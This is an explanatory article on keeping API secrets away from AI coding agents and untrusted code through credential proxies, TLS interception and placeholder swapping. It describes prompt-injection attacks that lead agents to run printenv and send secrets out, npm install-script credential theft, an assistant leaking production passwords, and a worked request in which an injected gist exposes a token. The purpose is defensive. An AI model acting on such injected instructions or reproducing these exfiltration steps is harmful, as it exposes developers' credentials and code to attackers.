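# How untrusted code and AI agents can use credentials without holding the secrets

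## Why a program that can read a secret can lose it

Software that uses an outside service, such as a code host, a payment system or a language model, usually has to authenticate, or prove its identity to the service. Most programs do this with an API key or an access token, a long random string that the service issues in advance and the program attaches to each request. (An API, or application programming interface, is the set of requests that a service accepts from other programs.) Such keys and tokens are bearer credentials, meaning that the service normally checks only the string and accepts it from anyone who presents it, including a thief.

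The usual practice is to give a program the secret and trust it to handle the secret safely. This is risky when the program is code from strangers or an AI agent, a system in which a language model works through a task by running commands and calling other software. Several arrangements let such a program make authenticated requests while keeping the secret out of its reach. Many of them depend on a proxy, a program that receives another program's requests and forwards them to their destination.

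### A coding agent with a GitHub token

Suppose a developer asks a coding agent to fix a bug and propose the change on GitHub. The agent needs a token with permission to write to the project, so the developer supplies one in an environment variable named `GITHUB_TOKEN`. An environment variable is a named value that a program receives when it starts. By default, a program passes all its environment variables to every program it starts, so the agent's shell, the test suite and the installation script of each downloaded package all get a copy of the token.

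When one of these programs calls GitHub, it puts the token in an HTTP header, one of the labelled lines at the top of a web request:

`Authorization: Bearer ghp_…`

TLS, the encryption behind every `https` address, hides that line from anyone watching the network, but the program that writes the header and the server that receives it both have the token in plain text.

Careful developers run the agent in a sandbox, an isolated environment such as a container or a virtual machine. The sandbox keeps the agent away from the developer's other files, but it does not protect the token, which the developer has deliberately put inside. If the sandbox has an open internet connection, any process in it can send the token anywhere.

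AI agents can also leak secrets through prompt injection, a risk specific to them, in which an attacker places instructions in material that an agent reads so that the agent follows them. The attacker doesn't need direct access to the agent. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) describes an outsider who plants instructions in a web page or document and waits for an agent to retrieve it. For coding agents, NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* lists malicious repositories, pull requests (proposed changes to a project), git histories and the instruction files that agents load when they start. A comment in a bug report might ask the agent to run `printenv`, which prints every environment variable, and to post the result to an address "for diagnostics". If the model complies, the command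 runs with every permission that the developer gave the agent. Kim and colleagues cite an attack of this type that reached private GitHub repositories. Asking a person to approve each command gives limited protection because, as NVIDIA warns, people get into the habit of approving without looking.

A malicious package can steal secrets without fooling a model. Package managers such as npm, which distributes JavaScript code, can run a package's own script during installation, and that script inherits the environment variables. In late 2025 the Shai-Hulud 2 attack used this mechanism on thousands of machines. GitGuardian, a company that sells tools for finding leaked secrets, rescanned the stolen data for its report *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026). It found 33,185 different secrets on 6,943 machines. At least 3,760 of the secrets still worked, and each of those was stored in about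 eight places on the same machine, so deleting one file would have achieved little. About 59% of the machines were build servers, which test and package code automatically, so the problem extends well beyond laptops.

Shai-Hulud 2 is one of several such attacks. Sonar's *Your secrets are leaking to AI coding agents* describes a variant, Mini Shai-Hulud, that looks for more than 80 environment variables and more than 130 file paths. In the s1ngularity campaign, a script in poisoned npm packages searched for GitHub tokens. According to Docker's *Coding agent horror stories the 29 million secret problem*, the script then looked for an AI coding agent already installed on the machine and handed the search over to it. The Russian-language article *Атака вышла за пределы GitHub* (2026) reports the security firm Aikido's findings on a campaign of 10 to 12 November 2026, in which attackers made malicious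 changes to 8,093 GitHub repositories. Most of the changes were to existing build workflows, and 771 repositories received an install-time script. The attackers' program searched environment variables and the memory of running processes, and sent what it found to remote servers or to Telegram. In one group of projects, the attackers reversed their changes after about 50 seconds, so an owner who inspected the repository later would have seen nothing wrong.

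Tokens can also leak without an attack. A coding agent's language model usually runs on the model provider's servers. The agent sends the model the developer's request, the files it opens and the output of the commands it runs, which the model uses to choose the next step. If the agent runs `printenv` to find out why a build fails, it sends any token in the environment to the model provider.

TechRadar's *'I leaked secrets'* describes one such case, which NordLayer, a network-security company, observed with its monitoring product. A quality-assurance engineer asked a coding assistant to review proposed changes to some software. The project's instructions directed the assistant to a configuration file containing a token for GitLab, a code host like GitHub. The file also held production passwords, a token for an internal human-resources system and credentials for a business-intelligence service.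 The assistant read the whole file in 10 separate sessions over three weeks, and each time the contents went to an external AI service. When it worked in a fresh copy of the project that lacked the file, it fetched all the computer's environment variables instead, which exposed more passwords. It then acknowledged the leak and recommended replacing the credentials. This is a single case from a vendor with a product to sell, but nothing about it is unusual. The task needed one token, and the easiest way to get it was to read the whole file.

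Two other sources suggest that the pattern is common, though neither measures how common. In an informal test, Kevin Roleke planted realistic secrets in six software projects and asked several coding agents to explore each one and help set it up. Every agent leaked at least one secret in every project, on every run. Users sometimes leak secrets themselves. *Cybersecurity AI (CAI) Dataset* (2026), a study of 230,935 recorded agent sessions, found people pasting the contents of `.env` files (text files that hold a project's environment variables) into the prompt, including a GitHub token, with a short note telling the agent to continue from a failed run.

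### How many secrets leak, and how quickly strangers use them

The largest count is of secrets that developers accidentally publish in source code. GitGuardian scans public commits (saved sets of changes) on GitHub. In 2025 it found 28.65 million new hardcoded secrets in about 1.94 billion commits, 34% more secrets than the year before. Such counts depend heavily on how the scanner handles false alarms. *Vulnerabilities, Secrets and Misconfiguration in the Highest-Exposure Docker Hub Images* (2026) reports that a popular scanner flagged secrets in 76.9% of the software packages it checked, but manual classification of 1,100 detections confirmed that the large majority were example keys, test data or material already public. GitGuardian filters its results with a machine-learning model and reran the same filter over its data back to 2021, so the growth rate is probably more reliable than the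 total. GitGuardian puts the precision of its results at about 99%, based on its own internal evaluation.

GitGuardian identified commits written with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, by a line in the commit message naming the tool as co-author. Over 2025, 3.2% of these commits leaked a secret, against 1.5% of all public commits. The monthly rate peaked in August at 31 secrets per 1,000 commits, about 2.4 times the human rate, and fell to 13 per 1,000 by December, level with the human rate. The yearly and monthly figures don't quite fit, since a yearly average cannot exceed its highest month, and GitGuardian may have counted them differently. Either way, the claim that AI-assisted code leaks twice as much describes the middle of 2025 better than the end of the year.

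The comparison also doesn't isolate the tool's effect. From April, the Claude Code commits contained about twice as many lines as the others for much of the year, which leaves more room for mistakes, and GitGuardian stresses that a person still decides what to commit. Publishing a secret in code also differs from having a token stolen from a running agent, though in both cases the secret is within reach of the tool that does the work.

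Once a key is public, its owner has very little time before someone tries to use it. Help Net Security's *Bots exploited leaked AWS key from Docker image in under 8 seconds* describes an experiment by Billy Tsouvalas and Nick Nikiforakis of Stony Brook University that measured this time. Over four months, they published 300 copies of a standard web-server image on eight public registries. (An image packages a program with everything it needs to run, and a registry is a site that distributes images.) Each copy held decoy keys for Amazon's cloud service AWS, for OpenAI and for Anthropic. The researchers advertised none of these keys, but the AWS ones drew more than 140,000 requests from over 5,000 internet addresses.

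The timing figures come from the first round, in which the researchers published 100 images, all on Docker Hub, the best-known registry. The median AWS key was first used 51 seconds after publication, and the fastest after 7.86 seconds. Strangers tried 93% of the keys within five minutes and all of them within fifteen. Docker Hub's download counter runs five to six minutes behind, so an owner watching it would usually have learned of the theft only after someone had tried the key. The researchers had also hidden alarms in the images that would go off if anyone ran them, and no alarm went off in this round. From this and other observations, they inferred that the bots list newly published images, download only the layers likely to contain credentials, and search those layers for strings that look like keys.

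Attackers took longer to exploit the OpenAI and Anthropic keys. Bots tested the OpenAI keys soon after publication and left them alone for weeks, until somebody ran 143 requests through a single key in under a day and emptied the account. The researchers suspect that whoever ran the bots had sold the working keys. A week without misuse after a leak is therefore weak evidence that nobody has the key. The experiment covered only public exposure. A token stolen through a prompt injection goes to one attacker, who may act sooner or later than the bots did.

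Owners are slow to cancel leaked credentials. More than 64% of the credentials that GitGuardian had confirmed as working in 2022 still worked in January 2026. The security firm Truffle Security retested 10,616 leaked AWS key pairs and found that 88% still worked, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover Thousands of Leaked AWS Keys*. Cleanup after a leak is too slow and too rare to rely on, which is the practical reason not to give the program the secret in the first place.

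### What to assume about each part

A threat model sets out which parts of a system an attacker may control and which parts the defender assumes are sound. Here, everything inside the sandbox counts as hostile: the agent, the packages it installs, the code it writes and every command it runs. A defence that works against hostile code also protects against careless code. This matters because an assistant that serves no attacker can still leak secrets, as the NordLayer assistant did when it sent out a file of production passwords.

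The assumption rules out some popular defences. Telling the agent never to reveal the token fails because the agent may be following someone else's instructions. A filter inside the agent's software that checks each command before it runs is also weak because, as NVIDIA points out, once a command has started another program, the agent software can no longer see or control what that program does. So the checks have to run beneath or outside the sandbox.

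The trusted parts are the proxy, the host machine that runs the sandbox, and the secret store, which holds the real credentials. Trusting the host includes trusting the isolation between it and the sandbox. If hostile code escapes onto the host, it can read the proxy's memory, and the credentials are no longer protected. This is one reason NVIDIA recommends a virtual machine with its own operating-system kernel over a sandbox that shares the host's kernel.

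A secret store can also fail to protect the secrets it holds. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (2026) reports that in June 2024 Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, disclosed unauthorised access to secrets that customers had stored for their hosted applications, and advised the affected customers to replace them. The disclosure shows the risk of keeping many secrets in one place, although it does not show that the intruders took or used every secret. GitGuardian reports a similar weakness at Smithery, a service that hosts tools for AI agents, where one bug made the keys of thousands of customers accessible. Moving a secret out of the sandbox makes sense only if its new location is smaller, simpler and better defended than the sandbox.

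### Three goals that need different controls

A hostile program can do three separate kinds of harm with a credential, and a safeguard that prevents one may not prevent the others.

A program that can read a secret can keep a copy of it. Holding the secret outside the sandbox prevents this. In the GitHub example, the agent sends its request without a token. A credential proxy, a program outside the sandbox that holds the secrets and adds them to outbound requests, inserts the `Authorization` header before the request reaches GitHub. `printenv` then has no token to print, a malicious package finds none in the environment or the project's files, and none reaches the model provider in the agent's text. This protection lasts only as long as nothing brings the token back into the sandbox, for example in a reply from the service.

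A program that cannot read a token can also have it sent to the wrong place, because the program still writes the requests and can address one to an attacker's server. A proxy that adds the token to every request would then deliver it to the attacker. Preventing this requires destination binding, a rule that a given secret may go only into requests for named destinations. An allowlist, which lets the sandbox reach only listed destinations, adds a second barrier and also protects things that are not credentials, such as source code. NVIDIA lists control of outbound connections as mandatory and keeping secrets away from the agent as recommended. That order makes sense for an agent whose working files are worth stealing even when they contain no keys.

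Finally, the program can misuse the credential at the service it is meant for. When the proxy adds a token only to requests for GitHub, a prompt injection can still make the agent delete a branch or copy a private repository into a public one, if the token's permissions allow it. Hiding the token and restricting where it goes don't prevent this, because the harmful requests go through the proxy to an allowed destination. The remedy is to limit what the credential can do, through narrow permissions at the service, proxy rules about which requests may pass, and human approval for the few irreversible actions.

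The decoy experiment offers some support for narrow permissions. In its second round, some of the OpenAI and Anthropic keys had restricted permissions, and Help Net Security reports that nobody ran up charges on any of them, although bots drained the unrestricted keys. It also matters where the limit is applied. TechRadar also describes a second case from NordLayer, in which a company's official connection for AI assistants appeared to block access to its internal documentation. An employee asked the assistant whether a newly created API token would offer another way in, and the token worked. The company had restricted one connection, but the documentation service still accepted any valid token that arrived by another.

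## Adding the credential at a proxy outside the sandbox

A credential proxy has to add a header to the program's request, but most services accept only HTTPS, so the program has usually encrypted the request before the proxy receives it. With an ordinary proxy, the program first sends a `CONNECT` request to open a tunnel to the service, then encrypts everything it sends through the tunnel. Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* explains that the proxy can't see or change the encrypted request.

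The usual solution is TLS interception. The program's encrypted connection terminates at the proxy, which reads and changes the request, then sends it to the real service over a second encrypted connection.

### One request from start to finish

TLS interception depends on certificates. A server proves its identity with a certificate, a file that ties its domain name to a public key. A certificate authority signs the certificate, and a client accepts it if that authority is in the client's trust store, the list of authorities it trusts. Before the agent starts, the operator creates a new authority for the proxy and adds it to the sandbox's trust store.

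Suppose the coding agent from the GitHub example has fixed its bug and now opens a pull request.

1. The agent's client program connects to the proxy and asks for `api.github.com`. Its first TLS message repeats that name, unencrypted, in a field known as the server name indication (SNI).
2. The proxy makes a certificate for `api.github.com` on the spot and signs it with the new authority's private key. The client finds the authority in its trust store and accepts the connection.
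3. The proxy decrypts the request and looks for a rule that matches the destination. Here, a rule pairs `api.github.com` with the developer's token.
4. The proxy deletes any authentication header that the program sent and writes the real one.
5. The proxy connects to GitHub and checks GitHub's own certificate against the public authorities. The client can't make this check, because it sees only the proxy's certificate. If the proxy skipped it, anyone able to redirect the proxy's traffic could pose as GitHub and collect the token.
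6. The proxy forwards the request and passes GitHub's response back to the agent.

Lens' *Credential Bindings*, the documentation for a platform that runs agents, describes nearly the same sequence, except that the proxy matches the destination before decrypting anything. That order is better because the proxy can refuse a forbidden connection without handling its contents.

The request leaves the sandbox like this:

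```
POST /repos/acme/shop/pulls HTTP/1.1
Host: api.github.com
Authorization: Bearer not-a-real-token
Content-Type: application/json

{"title": "Fix rounding", "head": "fix", "base": "main"}
```

GitHub receives this:

```
POST /repos/acme/shop/pulls HTTP/1.1
Host: api.github.com
Authorization: Bearer ghp_…
Content-Type: application/json

{"title": "Fix rounding", "head": "fix", "base": "main"}
```

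In this technique, called header injection, the proxy writes the authentication header itself, regardless of what the program sent. (An unrelated attack on websites has the same name.) The program can send a dummy value, as here, or no header at all. In a related design, the proxy looks for a placeholder, a particular worthless string, and replaces it with the secret.

Deleting the old header matters as much as writing the new one. If the proxy let the program's own header through, hostile code could supply a token for the attacker's GitHub account and upload the developer's source code there, all through an approved destination. The cloud company Modal shows the deletion in Modal's *Inject Secrets into a Sandbox with a proxy Sidecar*, which uses Caddy, a common web server, as the proxy. Two lines of its configuration do the work:

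```
header_up x-api-key {env.API_KEY}
header_up -Authorization
```

The first line overwrites the `x-api-key` header with the real key, and the minus sign in the second line deletes any `Authorization` header. The example handles both headers because services differ in which one they read, so an operator has to find every place where a given service accepts a credential.

A mistake in adding the credential usually breaks the request without leaking anything. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* reports tests that the security vendor Corvic ran on its own credential-injecting product. A call to GitHub succeeded although the calling code held no token, and a search of the sandbox's 20 environment variables found no secret. A call to FRED, an economic data service, returned a missing-key error because the product put the key in an `Authorization` header and FRED requires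 it in the URL. With only 16 probes, the tests show that the mechanism works but not how often it fails.

### Protecting the authority's private key

The sandbox needs only the authority's certificate, which is public. The matching private key must stay outside the sandbox, because anyone who holds it can make a certificate for any website, and every client that trusts the authority will accept that certificate.

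Hostile code that already controls a sandbox gains little from stealing a certificate authority's key if only that sandbox trusts the authority. But if ten sandboxes trust the same authority, an attacker who steals the key from one of them and can intercept the others' traffic can pose as GitHub or a package registry to all ten. If a developer has also installed the authority on a laptop to silence certificate warnings, the key works against the developer's browser too.

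Cloudflare, which runs sandboxes for its customers, creates a new certificate authority for each sandbox so that none is shared. Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) describes how a process outside the sandbox reads the requested name from the SNI field, makes a matching certificate and completes the TLS handshake. The private key never leaves a helper process that belongs to that one sandbox. Lens also creates an authority per sandbox, keeps its key only in memory, and destroys it when the sandbox exits. *secret proxy*, a small open-source program, simply loads a key that the operator generated earlier and saved in a file. That key lasts until someone replaces it, so the file needs the same protection as the credentials.

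A certificate authority's own certificate can also limit which domains the authority can sign for. If the limit is `api.github.com`, someone who steals the authority's key can't use it to impersonate a bank, although some clients don't enforce these limits.

Interception also lets the proxy read everything else in the traffic, including source code and the agent's conversation with its model, so it makes sense to intercept only the connections that need a credential. *Tracekit Box* (Ghosh, 2026), an open-source system for running agents in small virtual machines, does this. When an HTTPS destination has no secret, the proxy can read only the host, port and server name. Docker's product likewise decrypts traffic to the hosts for which it supplies credentials, according to *Docker Sandboxes*, a guide from Varlock, which makes secret-management software.

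A program doesn't need interception if it has a setting for the address of its service. The operator can point that setting at the proxy over plain HTTP, and the proxy opens the encrypted connection to the real service. Claude Code has such a setting, `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL`, and Modal's example works the same way. The program then doesn't have to trust a certificate from the proxy, which some clients reject because they keep their own list of authorities. But each setting covers only one service, and Anthropic notes that `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL` redirects only the requests to the model. An agent that also uses GitHub and a package registry will probably need interception for at least one of them. The plain HTTP traffic must also stay on the same machine or on a private, encrypted network.

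### Tokenizer and sealed secrets

Fly.io, which hosts other companies' applications, built an early and influential credential proxy to protect secrets from its own website. It ran its main service on Rails, a popular web framework, and considered that service the part of its system most likely to have a serious security hole. In *Tokenized Tokens* (July 2023), Ben Toews explained how the company kept new secrets out of that service and compared three existing approaches.

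The most common approach was to store secrets in the application's database, encrypted with a key from the application's environment. The application can decrypt every secret, so an attacker who takes it over can too.

A secrets manager such as HashiCorp Vault stores secrets in a separate system with its own access rules and a record of who read what. It can sometimes use a secret on the application's behalf, for example by signing a request to AWS. For most outside services it can't do this, so the application must fetch the bearer token into its own memory. Fly.io still recommended secrets managers because they record access and make secrets easier to replace, which limits the damage from a theft.

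The remaining approach was to write a separate service for each kind of secret and have the application ask that service to make the call. Each service would be small, perhaps a couple of hundred lines of code. Toews thought this was secure but tedious, because a large application needs many of them.

Fly.io noticed that nearly all of these small services would do the same job of putting a secret into an HTTP request, so it wrote one program, Tokenizer, to do that for any service.

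Tokenizer has a pair of encryption keys. Anyone can encrypt, or seal, a secret with the public key, but only Tokenizer holds the private key that opens it. When Fly.io receives a new API key, it seals the key, and the application stores only the sealed version. To use it, the application sends an ordinary HTTP request through Tokenizer with the sealed secret attached. This is the example in superfly's *Tokenizer*, the project's documentation (superfly is Fly.io's account name on GitHub), written out as a request:

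```
GET / HTTP/1.1
Host: api.stripe.com
Proxy-Tokenizer: <sealed secret>
Proxy-Authorization: Bearer trustno1
```

Tokenizer opens the sealed secret, removes the two `Proxy-` headers, and sends this to the payment company Stripe over HTTPS:

```
GET / HTTP/1.1
Host: api.stripe.com
Authorization: Bearer my-stripe-api-token
```

The sealed package contains the API key and rules for using it. One rule requires the caller to present a password, here `trustno1`. The package contains a hash of that password, which is a fingerprint from which nobody can feasibly recover a strong password. Another rule can name the hosts that may receive the key. Because the rules are sealed with the key, a thief who copies the package cannot loosen them.

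Tokenizer is stateless, meaning it stores nothing between requests. Secrets arrive with the requests that use them, so there is no database to steal or back up, and an operator can run several identical copies of the proxy. But Tokenizer keeps no list of sealed packages, so it cannot revoke a stolen one. The owner has to cancel the API key at the service, or change Tokenizer's own keys and seal every secret again.

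Fly.io designed Tokenizer for a web application that might one day be compromised, which is close to the situation of an agent in a sandbox. In *Sprites + Tokenizer*, a post on Fly.io's forum, a user asks how to use Tokenizer with Sprites, the company's agent sandboxes. The user had examined the network from inside a Sprite and concluded that the Sprite could not reach Fly.io's private network, where Tokenizer normally runs. Putting Tokenizer on the public internet would solve that, but the project's documentation advises against it because Tokenizer will also forward traffic to private addresses that outsiders should not reach.

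### Where to run the proxy

An operator can put the proxy on the host, in a sidecar (a helper container beside the sandbox), on each cluster node (a machine shared by many sandboxes), or on a remote server. A compromised sandbox can send requests to the proxy in all four cases. The placements differ in what else the attacker can reach and how much work they create.

| Placement | What separates hostile code from the secrets | What an escape to the machine exposes | Operating cost |
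|---|---|---|---|
| Host | The sandbox boundary, ideally a virtual machine | The proxy and the host's secret store | Low for one developer, especially when the sandbox product includes the proxy |
| Sidecar | The boundary between two containers | The secrets of every sidecar on that machine | One proxy per sandbox, each needing its own secrets and updates |
| Node | The sandbox boundary, and the proxy's ability to tell sandboxes apart | The secrets of every sandbox on that machine | One proxy per machine, with more complicated rules |
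| Remote service | A network connection | No stored secrets, though the attacker can still send requests as the sandboxes there | A server to keep running, encrypted links to it, and proof of identity from each caller |

Docker Sandboxes, a product for running coding agents on a developer's computer, puts the proxy on the host. Each agent runs in a microVM, a small virtual machine. According to Docker's *Architecture*, a request leaves the microVM carrying a dummy value, and the host checks its destination before the proxy fetches the real credential and writes it into the header. The agent has administrator rights inside the microVM, but those rights don't extend to the proxy's memory on the host. The drawback is that each agent needs memory and disk space for its own virtual machine and its own copy of Docker's container software.

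Ghosh also puts the proxy outside the sandbox, but with a narrower opening. Each virtual machine has no network card, only a vsock, which is a direct channel to its host. A separate proxy on the host answers each machine's outbound requests. Anthropic describes an equivalent for containers, in which the operator turns off networking and gives the container a single socket file that leads to the proxy.

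Modal's example runs the proxy as a sidecar, a separate container that shares a private network with the sandbox. Only the proxy's container receives the key. The operator gives the sandbox an empty list of permitted internet addresses, so the proxy is its only way out. Modal's test program, running in the sandbox, finds no key in its environment and fails to connect to the service directly. It then sends a request with an invalid key through the proxy and gets a normal reply. Modal still classes sidecars as an early test feature and restricts who can use them.

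Sidecars are common in Kubernetes, a system that runs containers across many machines. Kubernetes groups containers into pods, and the containers in a pod share one network address. *Caging the Agents* (Maiti, 2026) describes a sidecar design for nine AI agents at a healthcare technology company. Each agent sends its model requests to `localhost:8443`, where a sidecar adds the API key and forwards them. An attacker who takes over the agent cannot read the key but can still send requests through the sidecar, which limits their rate, size and destination.

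Maiti's abstract describes the architecture as deployed, but in the paper the sidecar is only part of a planned Kubernetes version. During the 90-day study, the agents ran on virtual machines, and even the most hardened version kept credentials in `.env` files. An audit found 12 API keys in a single agent's shell start-up file, which shows why the company wanted a sidecar, but the study provides no evidence of how well the sidecar works in practice.

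The shared network address also creates a problem that Modal's design avoids. Kubernetes applies its standard network rules to a whole pod, so if the sidecar is allowed to connect to `api.anthropic.com`, the agent is too. The agent could bypass the sidecar and send data to that service with an attacker's key. Preventing this requires an additional control that distinguishes between the two containers.

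Cloudflare's sandboxes are closest to the node placement. The customer's code for adding credentials runs on the same machine as the sandbox, in the runtime Cloudflare uses for its other small programs. This keeps delays short, but software that handles many sandboxes must always match each request to the right one.

A remote proxy gives the strongest separation because the machine running the sandbox stores no credentials that hostile code could steal if it escaped. Anthropic's version for cloud servers puts the agents on a private network with no internet connection, and firewall rules let them reach only the proxy. A remote proxy suits a company that runs code for many customers. A single developer is better off with the proxy built into a sandbox product, because a remote proxy is a server that someone has to maintain, and every agent stops if it fails.

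### How the proxy knows which sandbox is calling

If each sandbox should have different credentials, the proxy needs a reliable way to tell which sandbox sent each request. It cannot trust a name the program puts in the request, since hostile code can write any name.

On a single machine, a proxy can identify the caller by its connection. Ghosh's system gives each virtual machine its own proxy, so any request that reaches a proxy came from its virtual machine. Cloudflare's platform passes the sandbox's identifier to the code that adds the credential, so that code can look up the right key. The sandbox presents no password, which Cloudflare considers safe because the traffic stays on the machine. This argument holds as long as the platform supplies the identifier and no other program can reach the channel.

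A remote proxy has no private channel of this kind, so callers usually have to prove who they are. *secret proxy* requires a token in the `Proxy-Authorization` header and checks it with a central server before opening a connection. Tokenizer uses a password for a similar purpose. Both are bearer credentials, and hostile code in the sandbox can steal them. Replacing the real credential with a token or password is still worthwhile, because the stolen one works only at the proxy, under the proxy's rules, and the operator can cancel it when the sandbox shuts down. Until then, a thief who can reach the proxy from elsewhere can keep using the real credential through it.

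Fly.io has a stronger method for programs on its own network. As *Fly-Src* explains, the company's network proxy adds a digitally signed header to each request, stating the time and which machine, application and organisation sent it. The receiver checks the signature and, in Fly.io's sample code, rejects any header more than ten seconds old. A thief cannot use a sealed secret tied to one machine from anywhere else. The signature proves only where a request came from, so an attacker who can make a trusted program send requests still gets a valid signature. In *CapSeal*, Jin, Guo and Cheung (2026) propose a related protection, in which a local broker ties each permission to one session so that an attacker cannot replay it later. They have built a prototype and describe a plan for evaluating it, but report no evaluation results.

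The worst mistake is to let the proxy accept requests from any caller. Suppose a proxy at `proxy.example.com` adds the developer's token to every request for GitHub. Anyone who learns the address can then act on GitHub as the developer without ever seeing the token. This makes the address a bearer credential, and it is poorly protected because people put addresses in configuration files, logs and bug reports, and secret scanners don't look for them. Someone can expose a proxy by accident if they start it on a laptop and it listens on every network interface instead of only the local one. An operator should make the proxy unreachable from outside and also require callers to identify themselves. Varlock describes a remote broker that does both, since a caller without valid credentials cannot open the tunnel that leads to the proxy.

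### Protecting a proxy that holds every secret

A credential proxy holds many secrets in one place, as the stores at Hugging Face and Smithery did, and it constantly processes data from hostile code. Several measures reduce the risk.

The proxy can fetch secrets when it needs them instead of storing them. According to Docker's *Manage credentials*, its proxy can hold a reference to a secret in a password manager such as 1Password and retrieve the secret on the host. By default it keeps the secret for 55 minutes, but it can be set to fetch the secret for every use. Without such a reference, Docker stores secrets in the operating system's keychain. On Linux machines with no keychain, it falls back to a file that anyone with the right file permissions can read, so operators of servers without a desktop should check which one Docker is using.

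Fetching secrets on demand reduces what a thief can copy at any moment, but the proxy still needs a credential to fetch them. Varlock's broker uses a single service-account token. An attacker who steals it can retrieve every secret the account may read, so the account needs narrow permissions. Similarly, a thief with Tokenizer's private key can open any sealed secret, but must also obtain the sealed copies.

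It helps to divide the secrets among proxies or sandboxes. A sidecar needs only the credentials for its own sandbox. Docker's proxy can restrict a secret to one named sandbox, but secrets for services are available to all sandboxes by default.

The proxy should also be small, and the sandbox should not be able to change the proxy's settings. Caddy normally runs an administration interface on the local machine that lets programs rewrite its configuration. Modal's example turns this off with the line `admin off`. In a Kubernetes pod, where the agent and the sidecar share `localhost`, leaving the interface on could let the agent redirect the real key to an attacker's server.

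Even careful proxy code contains mistakes. Ghosh fuzzed the parts of Tracekit Box that read network addresses, the opening messages of TLS connections and other data from the virtual machine. Fuzzing means feeding a program large amounts of malformed input to find faults. The tests found nine problems, all of which Ghosh fixed. An operator who writes a proxy from scratch should expect similar faults, and has good reason to start from an established one.

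## Giving the program a placeholder instead of the secret

Header injection works even when the program sends no credential, but some programs won't run without one. Many client libraries stop with an error if they don't find an API key at start-up. Infisical's *proxied services*, the documentation for a credential proxy, warns that AI agents often refuse to attempt a request without a real-looking key. Some programs also check the key's format, for example that it begins with `sk-`.

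A second difficulty is that some services don't read the credential from a header. Telegram's interface for chat bots expects it in the middle of the URL:

`https://api.telegram.org/bot<token>/sendMessage`

Other services expect it in the request body, the part that carries the program's data.

A placeholder can solve both problems. The program reads this worthless string, usually from an environment variable, and copies it into the request as if it were the key. The proxy therefore finds it where the real key belongs.

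Placeholders also make keys easier to change. Daytona's *Secrets*, the documentation for a hosted sandbox service, describes a placeholder that stays the same when the operator replaces a key. Running sandboxes start using the new key within 30 seconds, without a restart.

### How Deno Sandbox swaps the key

Deno, best known for software that runs JavaScript, launched Deno Sandbox in February 2026. It runs AI-written code in small virtual machines on Deno's servers. The customer's own trusted program creates the sandbox and lists the hosts that may receive each secret:

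```
secrets: {
  OPENAI_API_KEY: {
    hosts: ["api.openai.com"],
    value: process.env.OPENAI_API_KEY,
  },
}
```

A request then goes through these steps:

1. Deno keeps the real key outside the virtual machine. Inside, it sets `OPENAI_API_KEY` to a random string that begins `DENO_SECRET_PLACEHOLDER_b14043a2`. A malicious package that runs `printenv` finds only this string.
2. The program reads the variable and sends the string to OpenAI in an `Authorization` header, as it would send a real key.
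3. The request passes through a proxy that, as Willison (2026), in *Introducing Deno Sandbox*, explains, recognises the placeholders. Because the customer approved `api.openai.com` for this secret, the proxy puts the real key in the string's place.
4. If the program sends the same string to `evil.com`, Deno leaves it alone, and the attacker receives a placeholder that no service accepts.

Products differ in what they do when a program sends the placeholder to a host that the operator hasn't approved. Daytona forwards it unchanged, and so does the cloud company Novita AI, according to its *sandbox secret*. Gondolin, a tool that runs code in virtual machines, blocks the whole request, according to its *Secrets Handling* documentation. Blocking gives the operator a useful warning, because a program rarely has a good reason to send a placeholder to an unapproved host.

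A secret's host list controls only where that secret goes. By default, Deno lets the sandbox connect to any address, so hostile code could still send source code to `evil.com`. If a Daytona secret has no host list, the proxy replaces the placeholder with the real value for every destination, including an attacker's server.

### Fixed markers, random placeholders and session tokens

For services it supports directly, Docker gives the program a fixed marker, `proxy-managed`, in place of the key. The marker is there only to satisfy the client program. The proxy adds the real key by ordinary header injection and never searches for the marker. Every sandbox can use the same marker, and an attacker gains nothing by stealing it. But a fixed marker fails if the program checks the key's format.

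Docker's custom secrets, which are still experimental, cover that case with a placeholder such as `sbx-cs-` followed by random characters. Docker's reference page *sbx secret set-custom* shows that an operator can specify `sk-{rand}` instead, which produces a random value with the prefix that the program expects. Here the proxy does search for the string, so the string must be distinctive. If it were a common phrase, the proxy would sooner or later find it in ordinary text and put the secret there.

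Placeholders, unlike header injection, let the program choose which credential to use for a request. If the operator supplies two GitHub tokens, one read-only and one able to make changes, the program can pick one by sending that token's placeholder. It can also make a request without a credential.

A proxy that only swaps placeholders doesn't change a request that has none. It therefore lets through a token for the attacker's own GitHub account, which header injection would overwrite. To block such tokens, the proxy needs an extra rule that refuses any authentication header without a placeholder it recognises. Docker's cloud sandboxes avoid the problem by combining the two methods, giving the program a placeholder but having Docker's proxy write the `Authorization` header itself.

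A third design gives the program a temporary token that works only at the proxy. When a session starts, the proxy creates a random token and gives it to the program as its API key. The program sends the token in the usual header. The proxy checks that the token belongs to a live session, then replaces it with the real key.

Some developers call this the phantom token pattern, a name that comes from OAuth, a standard for giving applications limited access to accounts. In the OAuth version, an outside application holds only a random string. A gateway at the edge of the company's network sends that string to the authorisation server and gets back a signed token containing details about the user. The gateway passes the token to the company's internal services but not to the outside application, which never sees those details.

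In a Hacker News discussion of Deno's launch (2026), one developer described a similar arrangement for language models. The developer's company gives each sandbox its own "virtual key", which an internal proxy maps to the real key. The proxy also totals each sandbox's usage, and a leaked virtual key doesn't affect the other sandboxes.

A session token serves the same purpose as the password that Tokenizer requires, and a thief can misuse it in the same way, but ordinary client programs already send the header that carries it. It suits a remote proxy, but a proxy that serves one sandbox over a private channel doesn't need it.

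### Where the proxy may replace the placeholder

The most important setting in a placeholder design is which parts of a request the proxy searches. Suppose the coding agent holds the placeholder `ph_7f3a…` for the developer's GitHub token. The operator has approved it only for `api.github.com`, but the proxy replaces it anywhere in a request. A prompt injection then persuades the agent to publish a gist, GitHub's name for a shared text snippet:

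```
POST /gists HTTP/1.1
Host: api.github.com
Authorization: Bearer ph_7f3a…
Content-Type: application/json

{"public": true, "files": {"notes.txt": {"content": "ph_7f3a…"}}}
```

The proxy replaces both copies, and GitHub receives this:

```
POST /gists HTTP/1.1
Host: api.github.com
Authorization: Bearer ghp_…
Content-Type: application/json

{"public": true, "files": {"notes.txt": {"content": "ghp_…"}}}
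```

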